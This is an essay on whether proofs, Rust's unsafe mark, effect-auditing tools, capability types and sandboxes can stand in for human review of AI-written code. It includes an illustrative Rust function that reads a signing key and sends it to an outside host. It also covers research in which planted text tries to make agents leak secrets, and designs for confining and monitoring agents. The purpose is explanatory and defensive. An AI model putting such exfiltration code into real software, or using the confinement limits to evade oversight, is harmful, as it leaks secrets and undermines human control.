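In *Prediction*, the computer scientist Martin Kleppmann (2025) writes that he would rather have an AI system prove its code correct than have people review it. He expects that people will eventually ignore AI-written code as they now ignore the machine code that compilers produce. It doesn't matter if a language model makes things up in a proof, because the checker rejects the proof and the model has to try again. He accepts that the difficulty then moves to specifications, which take expertise to read and write, but points out that a specification is far quicker to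 write than a proof.

Results since he wrote this in December 2025 support what he said about proofs. His comparison for specifications is less helpful, because a team that gives up code review needs to know whether a specification is easier to check than the *code*. For sorting it clearly is, since a two-line specification covers every sorting method, however long or intricate. For a queue shared by several threads, Tolmach and Klaus list questions that somebody has to answer before any proof can begin, such as whether items must leave in the order they arrived and whether a request for memory can fail. A code reviewer would have to consider the same questions, so writing them down isn't wasted effort, but it doesn't save much either.

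Keles doubts that some software can be fully specified. Correct behaviour is fairly clear for a database, but for a user interface it depends on taste and on what users want. He also wants people to stop calling software "formally verified" and instead name the properties they proved. The Ethereum Foundation has published recommendations for describing verification work more clearly, after people found unexpected gaps in SP1 Hypercube, a system with core components verified in Lean.

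Sometimes a team can avoid writing a specification because the old program already provides one. Theorem's *lf-lean* describes a tool that generates, from Rocq code, a theorem that any correct translation into Lean must satisfy. A similar tool for Zig and Rust would have suited Bun, where the new program was meant to behave like the old one. But it would also have required the new program to reproduce the old one's wrong answers.

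Kleppmann's case is strongest for properties that are the same for every program. A definition of "never reads memory it has no right to use" applies equally to an image decoder and a web server, so experts can examine it once, along with the model of the processor, and reuse both for millions of lines of new code. A specification of what a particular program should do is new each time, so the amount people have to read grows with the number of features. A team can at least keep these specifications in files that its agents cannot edit and have a person approve every change. Agents could then rewrite the code and the proofs freely, but they would need approval to weaken a specification.

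## Which risks does the unsafe mark miss, and can other marks catch them?

Rust's `unsafe` keyword marks only operations that could break memory safety. A program without it can still delete files, send secrets to a stranger or skip a permission check. In one broad benchmark from October 2026, memory safety accounted for about 13% of the security tasks that AI agents failed. Other kinds of mark can show an auditor which code uses files or the network, or stop code from using anything its caller did not pass to it. They don't help when permitted code applies the wrong formula.

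### Three harmful functions in safe Rust

Here is part of an invented web service:

```rust
#![forbid(unsafe_code)]

use crate::auth::User;
use std::{fs, io::{self, Write}, net::TcpStream};

pub fn clear_cache(dir: &str) -> io::Result<()> {
    fs::remove_dir_all(dir)
}

pub fn report_error(message: &str) -> io::Result<()> {
    let key = fs::read_to_string("/etc/service/signing.key")?;
    let mut server = TcpStream::connect("logs.example.com:80")?;
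    write!(server, "{message} {key}")
}

pub fn delete_account(accounts: &mut Vec<String>, _caller: &User, id: usize) {
    accounts.remove(id);
}
```

`clear_cache` deletes whatever directory its caller names, even the one that holds customer data. `report_error` sends the service's signing key to another computer along with an error message. `delete_account` receives the user who made the request but never checks whether that user is an administrator. (The underscore in `_caller` tells the compiler not to warn about the unused value.) The compiler accepts all three functions, and an auditor who searched for `unsafe` would find only the line that forbids it.

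The compiler is working as designed here. The Rust Project's *What Unsafe Rust Can Do* includes leaking memory, overflowing an integer and deleting the production database among the things that count as safe in Rust. The project considers it impractical to prevent such problems completely. Microsoft's *Safety Guidelines* for Rust programmers warn that the technical meaning of "safe" differs from the everyday one. For example, a function called `delete_database()` can be dangerous even though it is technically safe, and the unsafe `get_unchecked` is usually harmless when used properly.

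### 44 vulnerabilities and no memory faults

Experienced Rust programmers make mistakes of this kind too. Ubuntu, a version of Linux, now includes uutils, a Rust rewrite of the GNU Coreutils. Canonical, the company behind Ubuntu, hired the security firm Zellic to audit uutils. According to *Security audit of rust-coreutils* (Coopersmith, 2026), Zellic reported 73 findings in the most security-sensitive tools, seven of them critical, and 40 more issues in a second round on the remaining tools.

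In April 2026 Canonical disclosed 44 CVEs in uutils, most of them from the audit. corrode's *Bugs Rust Won't Catch* explains several:

- `install` deleted a file and then created a new one with the same name. Between the two steps, an attacker could put a link there that pointed to the system's password file, and `install` would overwrite that file instead.
- `chmod`, which changes who may use a file, has an option that protects the top directory, `/`. The code compared the text of the path with `/`, so the protection failed for `/../`, which leads to the same place.
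- `kill -1` should have asked which program to stop. The Rust version tried to stop every program the user could see.

None of the 44 was a memory fault. Over a comparable period, the C originals had several, including buffer overflows in `pwd` and `tail`. corrode admits that the audit may have missed some memory faults in the Rust code, and that the GNU developers have had 40 years to remove faults like the three above. Even so, the result illustrates well what Rust does and doesn't prevent. Ubuntu 26.04 still uses the C versions of `cp`, `mv` and `rm`, because the Rust ones had the same weakness as `install`.

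### What goes wrong in AI-written code

In *Last Secure Code Benchmark*, Wu, Ge and colleagues (2026) built 450 programming tasks from 150 real vulnerabilities. They removed the code around each vulnerability and asked an AI agent to write a replacement. The instructions described what the code should do but never mentioned security. Hidden tests then checked whether the new code worked and whether it withstood an attack.

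The six models tested produced working code for 73.6% to 91.3% of the tasks. The best of them, Claude Fable 5, produced code that was working and secure for only 25.1% of the tasks.

| Kind of weakness | Vulnerabilities | Attempts both working and secure |
|---|---|---|
| Memory safety | 24 | 34.3% |
| File names and paths | 24 | 24.3% |
| Injection, where a program runs part of its input as a command | 40 | 23.9% |
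| Loading stored objects from untrusted data | 7 | 19.0% |
| Access control | 24 | 18.3% |
| Input validation | 16 | 14.6% |
| Letting an attacker choose which address a server contacts | 7 | 2.4% |
| Revealing private information | 8 | 0.7% |

These percentages are much worse than one would expect from ordinary code, because every task contains a pitfall that had already led somebody to make a mistake. For comparison, *Securing AI-Generated Code* (2026) cites a study of 7,703 files in public projects whose authors credited AI tools. An automatic scanner found at least one weakness in 12.1% of them.

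Memory-safety vulnerabilities make up 16% of those in the benchmark. Agents did better on them than on the others, so they account for about 13% of the failed attempts, including attempts that didn't work at all. That is a rough estimate of the share of failures a memory-safe language would remove from this mix of tasks. But Wu and colleagues chose the mix to cover a standard list of serious weaknesses, so it doesn't show how often each one occurs in practice.

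For a particular team, the share depends mostly on which language it would otherwise have used. Python and Java are already memory-safe, so switching from them to Rust removes almost no memory faults, while switching from C could remove a large share. *Broken by Default* (2026) gave seven models security-sensitive tasks, some in C and C++, and found that memory faults were the largest group. In the tasks about requesting memory, 67% of the outputs were vulnerable, typically because the code multiplied two numbers to get a size without checking whether the product was too large to store.

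The other kinds of fault may also be more common in AI-written code than in human code. *What is the Difference Between Me and You?* (2026) reports that a scanner flagged 13,419 possible command injections in code from an OpenAI model and 2,243 in human code. But scanners raise many false alarms, and code from another model, Qwen, was closer to the human pattern.

Wu and colleagues offer a plausible explanation for the order of the table. A programmer can prevent a memory fault with a local check, and careful code usually includes such checks. Protecting private information requires somebody to decide what is private, which the instructions didn't specify. Adding one sentence that asked for secure code raised the success rate of three models by 15 to 21 percentage points and brought the rate for memory safety to about 50%, but it hardly helped with private information. Rust's compiler therefore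 helps most with the faults that agents were already best at avoiding.

### Code that compiles and does the wrong thing

Matsakis says that type systems can show the absence of bugs, "but not the presence of correctness". He quotes Greg Brockman of OpenAI, who in January 2026 called Rust a perfect language for agents on the grounds that code that compiles is approximately correct. Matsakis sees some truth in this, since Rust's rules help keep agents on track.

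`delete_account` shows why. Its type signature specifies a list, a user and a number as inputs. A version that checked the user's rights would have the same signature, so the compiler accepts the function with or without the check. An agent that misunderstood who may delete accounts would get no error message to correct it.

Matsakis has seen agents misunderstand his intentions in this way. He divides software development into design, construction and optimisation. Design means working out and stating clearly what the code should do. Types mainly help with construction, but they can also record part of a design if somebody puts it there first, and several of the marks described below do this.

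### Cargo Scan: marking what code does to the outside world

Cargo Scan, a tool from two University of California campuses, extends the idea of the unsafe mark to files, networks and other programs. Zoghbi, Thien and colleagues (2026), in *Auditing Rust Crates Effectively*, describe how it works. It reads a crate's source and compares each operation with a list of "effects", which fall into three groups:

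- unsafe operations, such as following a raw pointer or calling a C function
- calls to parts of the standard library that reach the operating system, such as those for files, network connections and starting other programs
- places where the code creates a function to pass around as a value, since another part of the program may run it later

The auditor then labels each effect safe, unsafe or "caller-checked". In the web service, the tool would flag the key and the network connection in `report_error`, and the auditor could label them unsafe immediately. Whether the deletion in `clear_cache` is safe depends on the directory, so the auditor would label it caller-checked. Cargo Scan then shows every place that calls `clear_cache`, and the auditor judges each one. If the function is public, the label goes into a file that other teams can use when they audit crates that depend on this one.

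This resembles a safety contract, since the label passes an obligation to the caller, but nobody had to write `unsafe` or anything else in the code. Zoghbi and colleagues give the example of rust-embed, which was supposed to read files only from a directory chosen by its user. In development builds, one of its crates passed unchecked paths to a file-reading function in another crate, so a program could read files outside that directory, and neither crate needed unsafe code for this.

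To measure the work involved, Zoghbi and colleagues audited hyper, a popular library for web connections. With its dependencies, it comes to 160,000 lines in 30 packages. If a function had an effect, they counted the whole function as code they had to read.

| Measure | Result |
|---|---|
| Packages with anything to audit | 17 of 30 |
| Share of a package's lines to read, median | 0.4% (0.2% in the paper's abstract) |
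| Share of a package's lines to read, mean | 13.1% |
| Effects that depended on the caller | 30.8% |
| Places to inspect for each of those effects, mean | 3.1 |

The median understates the work, because many packages had little or nothing to read and a few had a lot. The tool can show only the effects in dependencies that hyper's own calls can reach. In seven packages that Zoghbi and colleagues also audited in full, this cut the reading from 4,292 lines to 3,145. Reading 3,145 lines would take about six hours at 500 lines an hour, and judging each effect would take longer than reading it.

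The approach should work even better on simple crates. Of the 10,000 most downloaded crates, 3,434 have no effects of their own, and about 3% contain 85% of all the effects. Zoghbi and colleagues also report that Cargo Scan cut reviews of new crates in a commercial project from several days to a few hours, though this is their impression and not a controlled comparison.

Cargo Scan doesn't yet analyse what build scripts do during a build, and the arrayref attack worked through a build script. *Crustify* (2026) compared Cargo Scan with other counting tools on code that connects Rust to C libraries. In one set of this code, Cargo Scan reported 55 uses of raw pointers where another tool found 443, probably because Cargo Scan skips some recent Rust syntax with a warning. If a crate's configuration file doesn't state its version number directly, Cargo Scan reports no effects and finishes as if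 it had succeeded, so an auditor could easily think the crate is clean.

Even a perfect version of the tool would miss `delete_account`. The function only changes a list in memory, so it has no effect to flag, and its fault is a missing check. The tool also wouldn't help much with uutils. It would flag both file operations in `install`, but `install` is meant to change files, and the auditor would still have to notice what could happen between the two operations.

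### Code that can use only what it receives

Cargo Scan finds risky calls after somebody has written them. A stricter approach makes such calls impossible unless the code has received a capability, a value that grants the right to do something, such as write to one directory.

Rust programmers can already build simple capabilities with private fields. This version of `delete_account` requires one:

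```rust
mod auth {
    pub struct User { is_admin: bool }
    pub struct Admin(());

    impl User {
        pub fn as_admin(&self) -> Option<Admin> {
            self.is_admin.then(|| Admin(()))
        }
    }
}

pub fn delete_account(accounts: &mut Vec<String>, _proof: auth::Admin, id: usize) {
    accounts.remove(id);
}
```

Only code in `auth` can create an `Admin` value, because the value's single field is private. Other code has to get one from `as_admin`, which returns it only for administrators. An agent that forgets the check now gets a compiler error. The agent could still write another function that removes items from `accounts` without requiring an `Admin`, so `accounts` should be private too, in a module whose functions all require one. An auditor can then read these two small modules and ignore the code that uses them.

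This protection depends on memory safety, since unsafe code could turn any value into an `Admin`. Other marks therefore rely on the unsafe mark, even though it doesn't catch these faults itself.

Files and networks are harder to protect in Rust, because the standard library lets any function open any file the program has permission to open. *RustConf 24/Audit Rust dependencies*, a set of notes from a 2024 conference session, mentions an alternative version of the library's file and network functions. In libraries of this kind, code can open files only through a directory value passed to it. But an agent can still call the ordinary functions. A lint can ban those calls in a team's own crates, but not in its dependencies.

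### Capabilities for AI agents

Some researchers therefore have agents write in languages that can block the ordinary route. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) uses an experimental feature of Scala 3, a language Odersky created. The agent acts by writing short Scala programs, and the compiler checks each before it runs.

In this system, the type of a function lists the capabilities that the function can use. If the list is empty, the function can't write to a file, contact a server or affect anything else outside itself. The system puts secret data in a wrapper called `Classified`, which lets the agent work on the contents only with functions of this kind:

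```scala
val key = readClassified("key.txt")
key.map(k => k.length)             // accepted
key.map(k => { f.write(k); k })    // rejected, because it uses the file `f`
```

The result stays in the wrapper, so the agent can compute the key's length but can't print it. The agent can also send a secret document to a separate, trusted model to be summarised, and the summary also comes back wrapped. The user sees the contents on screen, through a separate output that the agent can't read.

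Odersky and colleagues tested two models in 131 trials each, in which the user or a planted text tried to make the agent reveal secrets. Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked secrets in two trials and MiniMax M2.5 in 11 without the wrapper, but neither leaked any with it. Both models are now old, but the protection doesn't depend on how well a model resists manipulation. Performance suffered little. MiniMax M2.5 solved 41.7% of a set of programming problems through the Scala system and 43.3% with ordinary tools, and three models did slightly better with Scala at customer-service tasks.

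People read the list of what the agent receives instead of the agent's programs. They also have to trust the compiler and a reusable library of about 1,000 lines. A library module's author can mark it `@assumeSafe`, which exempts it from the strict rules and makes the author responsible for its safety, much like `unsafe` in Rust.

Odersky and colleagues name several limits. If the agent is allowed to start another program, the compiler cannot control that program. An agent could also leak a secret slowly by varying how long its calculations take. And they do not try to ensure that the agent's answers are right.

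*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) does something similar in Haskell. In one example, an agent builds a bibliography that may include only entries from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The function that writes to the bibliography accepts only values of a type called `Trusted`, and only the function that fetches entries from DBLP can create them. If the agent invents a reference, its program doesn't compile. The agent could still pick a real paper unrelated to the subject.

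Other designs vary how an agent gets its permissions and how long it keeps them. In *LACUNA* (2026), a programmer leaves a gap in a program for a model to fill, and the generated code can use only the capabilities available at that point in the program. A model tricked by a planted instruction gets no extra permissions. *Lingering Authority* (2026) proposes permissions that end with the task that needed them. A monitor grants access to particular files or tools and withdraws it after an event the agent can't fake, such as the monitor's own tests passing.

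### Sandboxes as a check at run time

A sandbox can enforce similar limits on a running program written in any language. WebAssembly, a format for compiled programs, is a common choice. Each WebAssembly module has its own block of memory and can affect the rest of the computer only through functions that its host program supplies. WASI, a standard set of such functions, lets the host give a module access to a single directory instead of the whole disk.

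If the team compiled `clear_cache` and `report_error` into a WebAssembly module and gave it access only to the cache directory, `clear_cache` would work on that directory and fail on any other. `report_error` would fail at its first line, because the signing key is outside that directory. The same protection applies to a C library or a Rust crate whose unsafe code nobody has audited. A memory fault could damage the module's own data but not the host's, as long as the software that runs the module is correct.

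An auditor can then concentrate on the functions that the host supplies. But a sandbox detects a forbidden action only when the program attempts it, which may be while a customer is using it. A type checker would report the mistake before the program runs. Data also has to cross the boundary each time the host calls the module, which makes sandboxes awkward for small functions that a program calls constantly.

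Zhou and colleagues note that an operating system's sandbox usually gives a whole program one fixed set of directories. With capabilities, an agent that handles several customers could give each helper access to only one customer's files. They regard sandboxes and capabilities as complementary, and a team that expects its agents to probe their restrictions has good reason to use both.

### Reading the core and leaving the edges

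Teams can also decide what to read based on how much damage a mistake in each part of the program would do. Anthropic has described using this method on its own code. In Anthropic's May 2025 talk *Vibe coding in prod*, researcher Erik Schluntz explained how to use code in production without reading all of it.

Schluntz's team merged a change of about 22,000 lines, most of them written by Claude, into the software Anthropic uses for reinforcement learning, a way of training models through trial and error. According to BestHub's *Mastering Vibe Coding*, people spent several days planning the change and working out its requirements. They kept it mostly to "leaf nodes", parts of the program that nothing else depends on, and carefully reviewed the core parts themselves.

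According to jc-aiwiki's summary of the talk, people often manage work that they can't check in detail. A chief executive can spot-check an accountant's figures without being an accountant. Schluntz's team similarly designed the change so that they could judge it by its inputs and outputs. This doesn't work for technical debt, meaning shortcuts that make later changes harder, which people can currently detect only by reading the code, though in a leaf node the debt at least can't spread.

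The evidence is one success reported by the company that sells the model, with no count of the faults found later. It is also 18 months old, and agents have improved a great deal since. The idea still makes sense for technical debt, but it is riskier for security, because a leaf node can do harm even when nothing depends on it. For example, `report_error` is a leaf because no other part of the service depends on it, but it leaks the signing key.

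Capabilities could fix this weakness. If an outer feature receives only the data and output file it needs, its position at the edge of the program does limit the damage. The core's reviewers would also decide what each feature receives, and they could leave the feature itself unread with far less risk. In Rust, they would need a sandbox or a tool like Cargo Scan to make sure the feature gets nothing else.

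### A wrong price in permitted code

All of these marks work at a boundary where a checking tool can recognise the risky action without knowing its purpose. A call that deletes a directory looks the same in every program, and so does an attempt to pass a secret to a function that can use the network. The marks don't work when the same action can be right or wrong depending on what it means.

An example is the cryptocurrency lender Moonwell, whose customers borrow money against deposits. If the value of a deposit falls too far, anyone may repay part of the customer's debt and take some of the deposit in exchange. In February 2026, a faulty change made Moonwell value a token called cbETH at $1.12, when its market price was about $2,200. According to Protos' *DeFi, meet Claude*, customers lost 1,096 cbETH, worth about $2.4 million, and Claude Opus 4.6 co-authored the change. Moonwell was left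 with $1.78 million in debts that nobody would repay.

The figure of 1.12 is roughly the value of one cbETH in ether, another cryptocurrency. The code had apparently left out the last step, multiplying by the price of ether in dollars. It broke no rule about memory, files or networks. A capability system would also have let it set the price, because that was the code's intended function.

Blaming only the AI system would be unfair. Web3 Is Going Just Great's *Moonwell lending protocol suffers $1.78 million loss after second oracle misconfiguration* reports that Moonwell had lost almost $3.7 million to another pricing error three months earlier. A security auditor who first blamed Claude later said that senior developers could have made the same mistake, and criticised Moonwell's checks.

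More specific types might have caught this error. In Rust, a programmer could give each kind of number its own type:

```rust
struct EthPerCbeth(f64);
struct UsdPerEth(f64);
struct UsdPerCbeth(f64);

fn price(rate: EthPerCbeth, eth: UsdPerEth) -> UsdPerCbeth {
    UsdPerCbeth(rate.0 * eth.0)
}
```

If an agent left out the multiplication and returned `rate`, the compiler would reject the function because the result would be in ether, not dollars. The types let the compiler check a small part of the code's meaning. But an agent could also remove the error by writing `UsdPerCbeth(rate.0)`, which compiles and gives the same wrong price. Someone therefore has to read the few places where the code assigns a type to a number, just as someone has to read unsafe blocks.

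A run-time check could also help. Moonwell could have refused any price that differed from the previous one by more than half, which would have stopped a fall from $2,200 to $1.12 whatever the formula. But the same check would block a correct price during a market crash, and like every other mark in this section, it would accept a formula that was wrong by 5%. To catch that error, a person would have to know how to value cbETH or write a correct specification of the rule.
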